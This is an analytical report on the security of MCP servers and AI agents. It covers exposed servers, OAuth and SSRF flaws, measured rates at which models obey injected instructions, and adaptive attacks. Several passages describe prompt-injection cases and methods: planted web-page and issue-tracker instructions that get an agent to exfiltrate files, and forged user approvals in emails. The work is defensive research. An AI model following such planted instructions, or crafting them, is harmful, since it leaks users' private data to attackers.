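Zhou and colleagues started with 28,715 addresses from two search engines for internet-connected devices and kept the 7,973 that answered as MCP servers. Of these, 3,233 (40.55%) let anyone use their tools without a credential. Another 2,312 required a fixed token or API key. The remaining 2,428 used OAuth, a standard that lets a user give a program limited access to an account without handing over the password.

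An attacker who finds an open server can call its tools directly, without having to fool a model, but often there is little to gain. Most of the servers in a random selection the researchers examined were tests or demonstrations with no apparent sensitive data. One server, which a company had meant for internal use, exposed more than 5,000 customer records, including names, phone numbers and addresses. The researchers don't give the size of their selection, so we can't estimate how many of the other open servers hold similar data.

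Padilla's figure of 91.8% greatly overstates the share of servers that lack authentication, because it counts every server without OAuth, including some that asked for an API key or a fixed token. Padilla's discussion calls all of these servers unauthenticated. In the one scan that counted servers with no credential check at all, Padilla found 106 out of 464, or 23%. The two studies found their servers through different sources, which may explain part of the gap between 23% and 41%.

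Padilla also counted 687 tools that appeared to let anyone run operating-system commands on the server. The count relies on tool names, such as `run_command`, and descriptions, so some of these tools may do less than it implies. If a tool does let anyone run commands, an outsider can use it to take over the server and choose every response it returns.

Of the 464 servers in that scan, 193 had disappeared three days later. Those with the most serious flaws disappeared less often, with only 9 of 41 gone.

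Authentication matters less for response injection than readers might infer from these numbers, because it controls who can call a server, not what the server reads. An issue tracker that requires users to sign in can still return a planted comment. Missing authentication makes response injection easier mainly when the server has a tool that writes data, because an outsider can then plant text that other people's agents will read.

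### A flagged server is not necessarily an exploited one

Hasan and colleagues dropped every project with fewer than ten GitHub stars, which left 583, and their code-analysis tool found vulnerabilities in 42 of those. Half of the 42 had exposed credentials, such as OpenAI keys or GitHub tokens in published files. None of the vulnerabilities were in the 61 "official" servers, which companies maintain for their own products. Hasan and colleagues' two percentages are often wrongly given as shares of 1,899 servers, and Zhou and colleagues repeat the 5.5% that way.

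The figure for tool poisoning rests on far less data. The researchers drew a random sample of 83 servers and managed to scan 73 with a tool from Invariant Labs that checks descriptions for suspicious text. A rate of 5.5% means it flagged four servers. With a sample this small, the share of all servers that the scanner would flag could be anywhere from about 2% to 13%.

A flag means a program matched a pattern associated with a problem. An attack requires a real flaw that an attacker can reach and something worth taking. An exposed key is useless if its owner has already cancelled it, and a poisoned description does nothing on a server that nobody installs. Automated checks also raise false alarms. When Zhou and colleagues looked for flaws in how servers use OAuth, human reviewers rejected 54 of the program's 379 alerts.

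Confirmed attacks are harder to find. The US cybersecurity agency CISA keeps a catalogue of software flaws that attackers are known to have used. According to Digital Matters' *The First MCP Flaw in the KEV Catalog Was an Authentication Check* (2026), CISA added the first MCP flaw on 2 September 2026. The flaw was in LiteLLM, gateway software for AI models, where an authentication check could let through a caller it should have refused. But the catalogue lists flaws in software products, so it would not include an attack in which a correctly working server returned a planted comment.

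A clean scan also doesn't show that a server is safe. The scanner that Hasan and colleagues used reads tool descriptions, not source code. It did not flag a server for the game engine Godot that came with automatic approval turned on for sensitive operations. The researchers noticed this setting only when they installed the server by hand.

### Three abilities that combine

An attacker who can only plant text needs the victim's own tools to steal data. One tool has to bring in the attacker's text, another has to read something private, and a third has to provide an outbound channel for the data. Willison calls this combination the "lethal trifecta". Each ability is ordinary and useful, but a host that lacks any one of them can't leak private data to this kind of attacker.

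Zhao and colleagues looked for these three abilities in 12,230 tools. An AI model read the tools' descriptions and people checked its answers, which left 5,666 candidates. The researchers then tried these in a real host and confirmed 1,062. Of the confirmed tools, 487 could take in outside text, 406 could read private data and 190 could send data out. Only 19 had more than one ability. The confirmed tools came from 370 of the 1,360 servers, and two servers had all three abilities.

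The true numbers are probably higher, because about 30% of the servers needed accounts or tokens that the researchers couldn't easily get, and others would not run. The count of outbound channels looks especially low. Only six tools were counted as both taking in outside text and sending data out, but any tool that fetches a page from an address the model chooses can also send data, since the model can write the data into the address and the request will carry it to the site's owner.

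Even so, based on the confirmed counts, someone who picked five of the 1,360 servers at random would have about a 4% chance of getting all three abilities, and someone who picked ten would have about a 21% chance. Real users don't choose at random, and they are likely to want web access, files and email together. Many hosts also have their own tools. A coding assistant that can already read files and run commands may need only one more server, such as an issue tracker, to have all three abilities.

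### Three harmless servers in one host

Suppose a purchasing manager wants an assistant that can look things up, work with documents and send messages. The company's security reviewer receives three requests for MCP servers, each in a different month. The servers are modelled on ones that Zhao and colleagues tested.

| Server | What it does | Why the reviewer approves it | What it gives an attacker |
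|---|---|---|---|
| Fetch | Retrieves web pages | It reads public pages and changes nothing | A way to get text to the model |
| Filesystem | Reads files in the manager's work folder | It runs locally and sends nothing over the internet | Private data |
| Gmail | Sends email from the manager's account | It has no access to the manager's files | An outbound channel |

All three approvals are reasonable. The reviewer could read every line of code and find nothing wrong.

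The manager then asks the assistant to summarise the delivery terms on a supplier's web page. Someone has added instructions to that page for AI assistants to find the current price list and email it to an outside address. The fetch server returns the page. If the model follows the instructions, it uses the filesystem server to read the price list from the permitted folder, then uses the Gmail server to send the contents. No server has malfunctioned or exceeded its permissions. The reasons in the third column hold for each server alone but not for the servers together, because the model can carry text from any server to any other.

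Zhao and colleagues ran an attack through the same kinds of server in Cursor with approval prompts turned off, and it succeeded in 8 of 10 trials. Success depends heavily on the model, as GPT-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5 resisted this attack in every trial.

To catch the risk, the reviewer has to list the abilities of every tool in the host, not just the servers, and do so again whenever someone adds a server. Removing the fetch server, for example, would not keep outside text out if the Gmail server can also read the inbox, because anyone who knows the manager's address could still send text to the model. Removing Gmail instead would leave the fetch server, which could send the price list out in a web address. In both cases, the remaining two servers still have all three abilities between them. Zhao and colleagues also tested a Microsoft 365 server that could read and send email, and an attack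 using only that server succeeded in 3 of 10 trials.

### Whose permissions a tool call uses

A local server runs as the user who started the host. As Padilla notes, it inherits that user's files and environment variables, settings that often contain access keys. A remote server runs on its owner's computers and has no direct access to the user's files. It acts on outside services with either the user's credential or its own. If it uses its own, everyone who can call the server gets the same access.

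These permissions limit what an attacker who controls the server can do. An attacker who can only plant text is limited further, because the model can do only what the tools allow. Hasan and colleagues describe a server for Apple's Notes app that needed access to the Mac's entire disk just to read the app's database. Planted text could at most get the model to misuse the server's note-reading tools, but a malicious update to the server could also read the user's other files. The scanner didn't flag this either.

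Broad tokens work in a similar way. An agent needs to read only one project to answer a question about issue 214. If the user's token also permits changes to every project, including private ones, planted text can lead the agent to use that extra access wherever the server has a suitable tool. With a narrower token, the tracker would reject those calls even if the agent followed the planted text, so the protection doesn't depend on anyone recognising the attack. The drawback is that the user must work out in advance what the agent will need and grant more access when the guess is wrong.

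Many remote servers hold a second credential. Of the 119 OAuth servers that Zhou and colleagues examined closely, 81 connected to an outside service on the user's behalf. For example, a server for the note-taking service Notion signs the user in and then gets its own token from Notion. If planted text leads an agent to misuse that token, the server becomes a confused deputy, a program that an outsider tricks into using its legitimate access on their behalf.

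Zhou and colleagues cite research that found servers commonly reuse a saved authorisation regardless of who is calling. If several people share such a server, instructions injected into one person's agent could make it act with another person's access.

### Ordinary flaws that give an attacker more control

Conventional software flaws can let a server reach more than its reviewer approved. One example is server-side request forgery, in which an attacker gets a server to send a request to an address the attacker chooses. A server inside a company's network may be able to reach internal systems that the attacker can't.

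Stanciuc (2026), in *Google, JPMorgan and two governments fixed the same MCP flaw*, reports that five organisations have fixed this flaw in their MCP servers: Google, JPMorgan Chase, the database company Weaviate, France's digital directorate DINUM and the Indonesian city of Tangerang. The independent researcher Syed Anas Mohiuddin reported the flaw to all five, and much of Stanciuc's account relies on his description. He wrote that one JPMorgan tool checked addresses against an approved list, while a second tool on the same server fetched any address it received.

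The Google flaw is also listed in the US National Vulnerability Database, as *CVE-2026-14540 Detail* (2026). Google's server for connecting models to databases followed redirects without checking where they led. According to the entry, either an attacker or "a malicious data-driven prompt" could trigger the flaw. Planted text could therefore get an agent to make the server contact an internal system. A redirect could also lead to the attacker's own page, whose text might then reach the model as a tool response from a trusted server. Google rated the flaw 8.0 out of 10 for severity and recorded no reported exploitation in that rating.

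Mohiuddin argues that the problem is structural, because teams with no shared code or owner all made the same mistake. The five cases come from one researcher who was looking for this flaw, so they show that the mistake is easy to make, but not how common it is.

Akamai found flaws in MCP servers for Apache Doris, Apache Pinot and Alibaba's database service, including SQL injection and missing authentication. The Pinot flaw received the maximum severity score of 10. An attacker who can change a database's contents can plant text for the next agent that queries it.

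Hosts can inherit flaws from the software kits their developers use. In September 2026, The Hacker News reported that a malicious server could exploit a flaw in the official MCP Python SDK to redirect the sign-in process and collect the user's credentials (*Official MCP Python SDK Flaw Can Let Malicious Servers Steal OAuth Credentials*). Versions 1.30.0 and 2.2.0 of the SDK fix the flaw, but each application has to adopt one of them.

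Hosts start local servers by running a command from their settings. In April 2026 the security company OX Security reported that several AI products let outsiders influence that command and so run programs of their choice on the machine. OX wanted the official software kits to prevent this. Anthropic declined to change the design, saying that running the configured command is expected behaviour and that developers are responsible for checking what goes into it. That position is reasonable when only the user can edit the settings file, but much weaker for an online service that accepts settings from strangers, where a safer default in the kits would protect many products at once.

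### How the authentication rules changed

MCP began as a way to connect programs on one computer, and its first version required no authentication for remote servers. The first four rows of this table follow Zhou and colleagues' history of the specification. The last row comes from SC Media, which summarised Akamai's analysis a month before the release.

| Version | Main change |
|---|---|
| November 2024 | No mandatory authentication |
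| March 2025 | OAuth 2.1 becomes the framework for servers reached over HTTP; clients must use PKCE, a one-time secret that ties a sign-in to the program that started it |
| June 2025 | Servers must check that a token was issued for them, and clients get a standard way to find out where to sign in |
| November 2025 | Clients should preferably identify themselves through a document at a fixed web address; automatic registration remains mainly for compatibility |
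| July 2026 | The specification mandates OAuth 2.1 |

Zhou and colleagues call OAuth mandatory from March 2025, while Padilla calls it optional. Both are partly right, because the 2025 versions allowed servers to go without authorisation but expected those that used it over HTTP to follow the OAuth rules. The phrase "mandates OAuth 2.1" may mean the same thing for the July 2026 version, so a server without authorisation might still comply with it.

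New rules also don't change software that is already running, and newer software often keeps the old behaviour so that older programs can still connect. GitLab's *CVE-2026-9739* (2026) describes another flaw in Google's database server, which affected users who connected under the November 2024 version of the protocol. Google had added settings to limit which websites could contact the server but accidentally left in an older line of code that allowed all of them, so a malicious web page could reach the server through a visitor's browser.

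Zhou and colleagues tested 119 MCP servers that use OAuth and found at least one flaw in how each implemented it, 325 in total. The most common flaw, found on 114 servers, was letting anyone register a new program with any return address. An attacker can register a program whose return address is their own website, then send the victim a sign-in link. If the victim approves the request, the server sends the sign-in code to the attacker, who can exchange it for access to the victim's MCP session. The researchers didn't take over any real user's account, but they confirmed that servers accepted such registrations.

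The 119 servers are only 5% of the OAuth servers in the survey, and they aren't a random sample. The researchers could test only servers that allowed automatic registration, which is where the most common flaw occurs, so the rate among other OAuth servers may be much lower. The PKCE results are more informative because clients had been required to use PKCE since March 2025, yet 81 of the 119 servers accepted sign-ins without it or with a weaker form.

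Zhou and colleagues suggest that the rules changed too fast for developers to keep up, and that many built only what they needed to make connections work. That is plausible, but the paper's totals don't separate servers by protocol version, so we can't tell from them whether older servers are less secure than newer ones.

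## How often models obey injected instructions

Even when a host has all three abilities, an attack works only if the model does what the planted text asks. Models vary widely in how often they do. When Shaikh and Montaruli ran the same attacks on 18 models in July 2026, Claude Fable 5 obeyed in 0.4% of trials and Amazon Nova Pro in 49.7%.

### What the trials measured

The researchers tested the models in eleven frameworks and, for comparison, directly through OpenAI's API. Each combination faced 45 attack scenarios, for a total of 9,720 trials. 268 trials couldn't run, mostly because some frameworks don't support GPT-5.5, and 237 ended in errors, leaving 9,215 to score.

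In each trial, the user made a harmless request to an agent connected to two MCP servers. The legitimate server had tools for handling files and making web requests, and the malicious one supplied the attacker's text. The agent could also read a folder containing a fake secret. A test server stood in for the attacker's website and recorded every request it received.

An attack counted as successful if the agent read the planted file, put the secret or the test server's address in a tool call, or contacted the test server. By this definition, 2,113 attacks succeeded, or 22.9%. The evidence was stronger in some trials than in others:

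| Evidence of success | Trials | Share of scored trials |
|---|---|---|
| The secret reached the test server | 255 | 2.8% |
| A request reached the test server without the secret | 487 | 5.3% |
| The agent did what the attacker asked, but the test server recorded nothing | 1,371 | 14.9% |

So the agent contacted the test server in 742 trials, or 8.1%. In nearly all of the other 1,371, the design of the test ruled out such contact, so they shouldn't be counted as failed attacks. In 1,067, the agent called a tool on the malicious server itself, which logged the call and returned a canned reply without contacting the test server. In another 290, the agent read the planted file, which involves no network traffic. In the last 14, it used a tool that the scenario had forbidden.

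A real attacker would run the malicious server and would already have whatever the agent put in those 1,067 calls. Adding them to the 742 gives 1,809 trials, or 19.6%, in which something reached the attacker's side, though not always the secret. A call counted even if it contained only the test server's address, and the paper doesn't report how many of these calls also contained the secret. The true rate of theft is therefore between 2.8% and 14.3%.

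The measurements look reliable. A second run of all the trials gave an overall rate within 0.1 percentage points of the first, and 93.5% of trials got the same verdict both times. The researchers also reread 1,259 transcripts by hand.

### Which models obeyed

| Model | Successful attacks / scored trials | Rate |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 2 / 465 | 0.4% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 8 / 530 | 1.5% |
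| Claude Sonnet 5 | 10 / 527 | 1.9% |
| DeepSeek-R1 | 19 / 534 | 3.6% |
| Gemma 3 27B | 22 / 534 | 4.1% |
| GPT-5.5 | 44 / 354 | 12.4% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 66 / 530 | 12.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 77 / 530 | 14.5% |
| Mistral Large 2 | 114 / 527 | 21.6% |
| GLM-5 | 129 / 530 | 24.3% |
| Llama 4 Scout | 133 / 473 | 28.1% |
| Qwen3-Next-80B | 159 / 533 | 29.8% |
| Ministral 3 14B | 183 / 533 | 34.3% |
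| GPT-OSS-120B | 201 / 527 | 38.1% |
| Mistral Large 3 | 233 / 533 | 43.7% |
| DeepSeek-V3.2 | 233 / 529 | 44.0% |
| Llama 4 Maverick | 235 / 533 | 44.1% |
| Amazon Nova Pro | 245 / 493 | 49.7% |

Fable 5's score excludes 68 trials in which a content filter blocked the request before the model produced anything. It seems fair to count those as resisted attacks, since nothing leaked, and doing so leaves the rate at 0.4%.

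The low rates for DeepSeek-R1 and Gemma 3 are harder to interpret because the study didn't test whether each model could complete the tasks without an attack. A model that rarely makes a working tool call will look resistant whether or not it would obey injected instructions. Both models had exactly the same success rate in each of nine frameworks. That would be surprising if their responses depended on the content of each attack, but not if they seldom got as far as calling a tool.

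Newer models are not always safer. Anthropic's recent models obeyed injected instructions far less often than its older ones, but Mistral Large 3 obeyed twice as often as Mistral Large 2, and more often than the much smaller Ministral 3. Shaikh and Montaruli think the most likely explanation is how much effort each company puts into safety training. They acknowledge that their scenarios come from published techniques, so some models' training data may have included similar attacks.

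Opus 4.8 explicitly refused 223 times, citing the poisoned description. Claude Sonnet 5 was less consistent, and in 4 of its 10 failures it identified the text as a prompt injection but still made the attacker's tool call. Four cases are too few to estimate how common this is, but they show that a warning in the model's output doesn't prove the model refused to make the call.

Earlier benchmarks reported higher figures. MCPTox, a 2025 benchmark that tested 20 agents with tools from 45 real MCP servers, had a top success rate of 72.8%. According to Shaikh and Montaruli, it counted an attack as successful when the model produced the attacker's call, whether or not the call ran. Because 72.8% is the worst result, it should be compared with Nova Pro's 49.7%, not the 22.9% average. But the two studies used different models and attacks, so the lower rate isn't evidence that models improved.

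### Instructions in tool responses

Most of this evidence concerns tool descriptions. The 26 scenarios that target them produced 1,460 of the 2,113 successes. Attacks in the other 19 scenarios succeeded in 653 of 3,856 trials (17%). Those scenarios use several entry points, and at least four also put the injected text in descriptions, so 17% isn't a rate for tool responses either.

The study lists injection through tool results as an attack type but doesn't report separate results for it. The closest type it reports is "confused deputy", one of the types that the researchers deliver outside the tool description. It succeeded in 161 of 627 trials (25.7%), close to the 27.2% for poisoned descriptions. This suggests that moving the text out of the description doesn't make an attack much weaker, though the two groups of scenarios also differ in other ways.

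Errico, Ngiam and Sojan (2025), in *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, tested an attack delivered through a tool response. They built a remote server with one tool to look up documentation and another to send feedback. The feedback tool returned an ordinary acknowledgement with a reference number, followed by a demand, presented as company policy, for the user's settings files and connection details. The agent was to send these back through the same tool, so the attacker needed no other outbound channel and could ask for more in each new response.

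Several commercial agents complied, but the paper doesn't name them or give a rate. The feedback tool's description also asked for detailed logs and output from every connected server, so the agents may have been responding partly to the description.

*MCPXKIT* (Guo, Liu and colleagues, 2025) presents a toolkit of MCP attacks and reports how often they worked, but doesn't name the model tested. An instruction in a tool's return value worked in nine of ten runs, and one hidden in a web page worked in eight. Attacks through descriptions that made the agent read or change files worked in nine or ten. Guo and colleagues suggest that models obey tool results more readily than text from a web page because they treat tool results as verified feedback from the system. A difference of one run in ten is too small to support that. With so few runs, the true rate for the return-value attack could be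 anywhere from about 55% to nearly 100%.

In larger tests of injection through tool responses outside MCP, Lee and colleagues measured success rates of 20–42% for one attack. Dziemian and colleagues found a rate of 4.82% in tool-calling scenarios, where most attacks also had to stay concealed. These results can't be combined into one rate for response injection, so an operator who wants a number has to test the specific model with the tools it will use.

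An agent that refuses every injected instruction can still do harm by acting on false data. Choi, Kim and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents*, gave agents false data that they mistook for trusted data. For instance, part of a visitor's comment might look like a field that the issue tracker had filled in. The researchers used such data to make browser agents, including Claude in Chrome, click where the attacker wanted, and to run code through Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI. Most of the rates above don't include these attacks.

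### Whether the host or the model matters more

Huang and colleagues tested seven hosts and concluded that the choice of host matters more than the choice of model. Shaikh and Montaruli attributed all the deliberate resistance they saw to the model. The two studies compared different kinds of software, so their conclusions don't necessarily conflict.

| | Huang and colleagues | Shaikh and Montaruli |
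|---|---|---|
| Software compared | Seven finished applications | Eleven frameworks and one plain interface |
| Models | Mostly Claude Sonnet 4.5, but several default models in Cursor | 18 models, nearly all in every framework |
| Held constant | Four attacks | 45 scenarios, the system prompt and the tools |
| Free to vary | The host's own instructions, dialogs and warnings, and Cursor's models | How the framework presents tools and carries out calls |
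| Results | 28 | 9,215 |

The same study's code audit confirmed that a framework mostly passes text along. A finished host adds its own system prompt, approval prompts and sometimes filters, so hosts may well have a large effect on how often models obey injected instructions, while frameworks have little.

However, the evidence for a large host effect is weak. Cursor accounted for four of the five "unsafe" results, but it also ran different models from the other hosts. Only one of the 24 results from the other hosts was unsafe. In most of the safe results, the model refused before the host had to act, which also suggests that the results depended on the model.

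The evidence that frameworks don't matter also needs qualifying. Nine of the twelve setups had overall rates between 23.4% and 26.1%, but the other three did not:

- Pydantic AI had a rate of 16.6% because it refuses to load two tools with the same name. This stopped 250 trials before the model saw anything. In the rest, the rate was 25.0%, like the others.
- AG2 had a rate of 4.6% because it rarely completed the outgoing calls the models asked for.
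- smolagents had a rate of 34.4%. It presents tools as pieces of Python code, which seems to weaken safety training based on more conventional tool definitions.

None of these differences came from a deliberate defence, but they affected what an attacker could achieve. Averages also hide differences for individual models. Across the nine similar setups, the attack success rate varied by about 10 percentage points for a typical model and by 36.5 for Llama 4 Maverick.

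Anthropic's tests of a single model, Claude Opus 4.6, are better evidence that the surroundings matter. VentureBeat reported the results in February 2026. In a restricted coding environment, none of 200 attempts succeeded. When the model operated a graphical interface with extended reasoning turned on, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and the rate reached 78.6% by the 200th attempt. Anthropic's safeguards reduced the latter figure to 57.1%.

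So for a developer building an agent from a framework, the choice of model matters far more than the choice of framework. It is still unclear whether the same is true of finished hosts. Finding out would require running the same models in each host, with the same tools and attacks.

### What developers report about newer models

Anthropic's published results have improved quickly. Its system cards now use Gray Swan's newer rounds of attacks instead of an older benchmark on which Claude models had scored almost perfectly, TechFeed reports. In the newer rounds, attackers with fifteen attempts succeeded 5.5% of the time against Opus 4.8, 2.8% against Fable 5 and 2.0% against Opus 5, according to The Decoder. Fable 5.1 continued the trend at 1.0%, though on a larger set of attacks.

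How well a model resists injected instructions doesn't depend only on its general ability. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Opus 5 describes it as no more capable overall than Fable 5, but Opus 5 resisted injection slightly better.

No attack succeeded against Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios. If we treat these as independent trials, the true success rate could still be as high as about 2%, which is high enough to matter for an agent that reads thousands of pages.

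OpenAI added injection results to its GPT-5.6 system card in August 2026. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) gives a failure rate of about 0.05% when the company's automated attacker typed directly into the chat with the largest version, Sol. When the attack arrived through tools or outside content, the rate was 3.77% for Sol, 3.32% for Terra and 2.94% for Luna. The direct figure is therefore a poor guide to how often an agent fails when it reads someone else's text.

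Other organisations have tested Google's models. Gemini 2.5 Pro was the easiest target in Gray Swan's competition. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports attack success rates as high as 92% for Gemini 3 Pro and GPT-5.1 in a later Gray Swan benchmark that used very strong attacks.

### Why a fixed set of attacks gives low numbers

Shaikh and Montaruli tested every model on the same 45 scenarios. This makes the comparison fair, but a real attacker can tailor the attack to the target. A developer can also train a model to recognise known attacks, which will improve its score more than its resistance to new ones. Ye and colleagues suspected something like this when standard injections failed on most of the models they tested.

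Attackers can also simply try again. If each attempt has the same independent chance p of working, the chance of at least one success in n attempts is:

1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

In the benchmark with very strong attacks, a single attempt succeeded 4.7% of the time against Opus 4.5. The success rate rose to 33.6% after ten attempts and 63% after a hundred. If attempts were independent, those rates would have been 38% and 99%. They evidently aren't independent, probably because attacks succeed quickly on some targets and hardly ever on others.

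An adaptive attacker uses the result of one attempt to write the next. In *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections*, Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026) tried this on an email assistant running Claude Sonnet 4.6. The user had asked only for a reading task, such as summarising the inbox, and the attack succeeded if the assistant sent an email. A fixed set of emails, each falsely claiming that someone had already authorised a reply, succeeded 0.67% of the time.

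The researchers then had a second copy of Sonnet 4.6 write the emails. After each failure, it received an analysis of the assistant's response and wrote a new version. It had up to 15 tries in each of three separate runs and succeeded in 96.7% of 150 scenarios. The most common successful approach was to include a forged earlier message from the user, which the assistant treated as a genuine instruction.

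Repeated feedback explains only part of this increase, since the attacking model's first email already worked 61.4% of the time. The attacking model had a copy of the assistant's system prompt and the researchers' advice on which claims the assistant was most likely to trust, so much of the adapting happened before the first attempt. The best emails also worked unchanged on other models, succeeding 92.6% of the time against Gemini 3 Pro, 89.3% against GPT-5.2 and 63.3% against GPT-5.4.

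When the researchers told the attacker not to forge approvals and to rely on arguments, such as the harm a delay would cause, it rarely succeeded against Sonnet 4.6. It succeeded 79.0% of the time against GPT-5.2, though the attacker sometimes broke the rule by claiming that the user had agreed.

These numbers don't show that an adaptive attacker can make a current agent do whatever the attacker wants. The assistant had instructions to send emails without asking when that seemed appropriate, and the attacker often wanted only a routine confirmation, which is a much less unusual request than one for a password.

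Adaptive attacks on coding agents have had far less success. VentureBeat reports that Gray Swan's adaptive attack tool succeeded on 7.03% of single attempts against Opus 4.8, and on 2.09% with safeguards on. Digital Applied (2026), a consultancy that reviewed the system card, puts the figure for Fable 5 at 0.41%. The difference between 0.41% and 96.7% is probably due more to what the attackers asked for, and whether an honest person might have asked for the same thing, than to the attackers' skill.

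### When an honest request looks the same

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian argue that this last problem will remain even if models learn to ignore planted commands. They start from contextual integrity, Helen Nissenbaum's theory of privacy, which holds that whether a flow of information is appropriate depends on its sender, its recipient, its subject, the type of information and the conditions under which it is shared. An attacker can lie about any of these. For example, a fraudulent refund request can cite a department head's approval that would make the request legitimate if it were real.

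Their proof compares two situations that look identical to the agent after it has made every check available to it. Suppose a comment on issue 214 states that Priya has approved sending the export file to a contractor. In one situation she has, and in the other an attacker made it up. Let p be the probability that the agent sends the file. Since the agent has the same information both times, p must be the same both times, so:

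chance of obeying the attacker + chance of refusing the genuine request = p + (1 − p) = 1

An agent that never accepts the false claim must always refuse the true one. Under any policy, at least one of the two errors, accepting the false claim or refusing the true one, has a probability of at least one half.

The difficulty here is missing information. Identifying exactly which words came from the visitor still wouldn't show a model whether Priya had agreed. The proof in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* depends instead on how models represent text internally.

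The theorem is narrower than the paper's title suggests, because it applies only where two such situations exist. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian state that it doesn't prove they exist in every deployment. If the agent can check the approval against a trusted record, the situations no longer look the same and the theorem doesn't apply. The theorem also doesn't show how often an agent will meet such a pair. An operator might be willing to have the agent refuse a few genuine requests a month so that it never sends a file to a stranger.

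Shaikh and Montaruli worry that models could become easier to hijack as they get better at following instructions, and they cite the paper as an impossibility result that supports this. The theorem doesn't show that, because it is about what an agent can verify, not how obedient it is. Shaikh and Montaruli's own measurements are mixed, since Mistral's newer model did worse and Anthropic's newer models did much better.

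The practical disagreement is over how much an agent can verify. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian expect unverifiable claims to become more common as agents work with less supervision, because each check covers only some of the claims an attacker could make. For example, an agent can use the issue tracker to confirm which account posted the comment, but not what Priya told a colleague on the phone. The agent could ask her, but that would mean another interruption.

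## What an attack on a live system needs to succeed

A model can obey a planted instruction and still do no harm, because the host has no email tool, the user refuses the call, or the company's network blocks the address. For the comment on issue 214 to end in a theft, seven conditions have to hold, in this order:

| Condition | What the attacker must know | What usually stops the attack here |
|---|---|---|
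| The attacker places text where a tool will read it | Which pages, tickets or projects the victim's agent reads | No agent ever fetches the text |
| The tool returns the text intact | Roughly how the tool shortens or reformats what it reads | A length limit, a summary or a filter |
| The model obeys | What the user is likely to ask, and ideally which model is running | The model ignores the instruction or reports it |
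| A suitable tool is available | What the host's tools can do | The host has no tool for the action |
| The call is permitted | What the user's credentials cover, and whether the host asks first | A narrow token, or a user who refuses |
| Data leaves, or the damage is done | A place that the agent can write to and the attacker can read | Read-only access or a blocked connection |
| Nobody intervenes in time | How soon anyone will look | Someone cancels the payment or changes the stolen password |

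Some sources are harder to place text in than others. Zhang and colleagues sorted their 20 servers into four groups: public web pages, browser sessions, collaboration services that require a login, and cloud infrastructure. The groups differ mainly in how much an attacker controls and where the text comes from. Anyone can publish a web page, and outsiders can often get text into a company's infrastructure by causing error reports or log entries that the company collects there. In either case, the attacker then has to wait for an agent to fetch the text.

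An attacker who knows the host's tools can write more effective instructions. The most successful payloads in Shaikh and Montaruli's study named a legitimate tool, specified exactly what to take and where to send it, and gave an official-sounding reason. The researchers had set up the tools themselves, so they knew the names. An attacker can look up the tool names of a popular server in its published code, but has to guess which servers a particular victim has connected.

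Permission can depend on the access token, the host's approval prompt and a confirmation question from the server. The server's question is the least reliable of these. Supabase, a company that hosts databases, warns in its documentation that such questions don't replace the host's approval and that some hosts have rules that answer them automatically.

Some tools satisfy several conditions at once. If an agent can run commands on the user's computer, a single command can start a program that reads private files and opens its own connection to the attacker. The attacker then needs no email tool and doesn't have to know which other servers the user has connected.

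### The chance per exposure

Call each occasion on which a model reads the planted text an exposure. By then the first two conditions already hold, so the chance that an exposure ends in harm is the product of the other five:

P(harm) = P(model obeys) × P(suitable tool | obeys) × P(call permitted | so far) × P(data leaves | so far) × P(nobody intervenes | so far)

The vertical bar means "given that", and "so far" means that every earlier condition has held.

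Here is an illustrative example with invented numbers. Suppose the model obeys 0.5% of the time, the host or user permits 40% of the resulting calls, and an outbound channel is open in 50% of those cases. Suppose also that a suitable tool is always available and nobody intervenes. Then:

0.005 × 0.40 × 0.50 = 0.001, or 0.1% per exposure

If 1,000 exposures are independent, the chance that at least one succeeds is 1 − 0.999¹⁰⁰⁰, or 63%. An attacker could get that many from 1,000 support tickets, or from one comment that 1,000 developers' agents read. If the operator closes most outbound channels, so that the last factor falls from 50% to 5%, the chance of success falls to 0.01% per exposure and 9.5% over 1,000 exposures.

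Cutting obedience or permission to a tenth would have had the same effect in the calculation. But an attacker can raise the chance that the model obeys or the user approves by writing a better instruction, while no wording will open a connection that the network blocks.

Measuring each factor separately and multiplying the averages can give the wrong answer. Suppose half of the planted texts contain a blatant request, which the model obeys 0.1% of the time and users would permit 10% of the time. The other half contain a request that fits the user's task, with rates of 0.9% and 70%. The averages are still 0.5% and 40%. But nine in ten of the calls that reach a user now come from the second half, so users permit 64% of them, and the chance of harm per exposure is 0.16% instead of 0.1%.

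### Why exposures are not independent

The 63% figure assumes that each exposure is independent of the others. Models do vary between runs, as Willison (2025) points out in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, but not much when the text and setting stay the same. Shaikh and Montaruli ran all their trials twice, and the two runs gave the same verdict 93.5% of the time. If every trial had had the same 22.9% chance of success in each run, only about 65% of the verdicts would have matched. Most of the variation is therefore between combinations of model, framework and attack, so an attack that failed once on a given setup will probably fail there again.

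Suppose one installation in ten is vulnerable, with a 1% chance of theft per exposure, and the other nine are immune. The average chance is still 0.1% per exposure. An operator with one installation and 1,000 exposures now has about a 10% chance of suffering any theft, rather than the 63% the simple formula gives, but an operator whose installation is vulnerable can expect around ten thefts. An attacker who spreads 1,000 exposures over 1,000 different installations still has a 63% chance of at least one success. The simple formula can therefore greatly overstate one operator's risk of any theft while estimating the attacker's chances quite well.

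Other kinds of dependence help the attacker. Someone who sees an attempt fail can rewrite the text, and the adaptive attacks on email assistants show how much that can help. One success can also make later ones easier. According to SmarterArticles' *Your AI Agent Will Be Compromised* (2026), attackers have begun planting malicious configuration files that agents load and trust in later sessions. Once such a file is in place, the attacker no longer has to get the original text in front of the model.

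### The GitHub issue (May 2025)

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes an attack through GitHub's official MCP server. The victim had several private repositories and a public one containing a Pac-Man game. Anyone with a GitHub account can open an issue on a public repository, so the researchers opened an issue containing instructions for an AI agent. Then, acting as the owner, they asked Claude Desktop, running Claude 4 Opus, to look at the project's open issues.

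The server returned the issue intact, and the model followed the instructions in it. It read the private repositories and opened a pull request (a proposed change to a project's files) on the public one. The pull request made public the names of private projects and the owner's salary and plan to move to South America.

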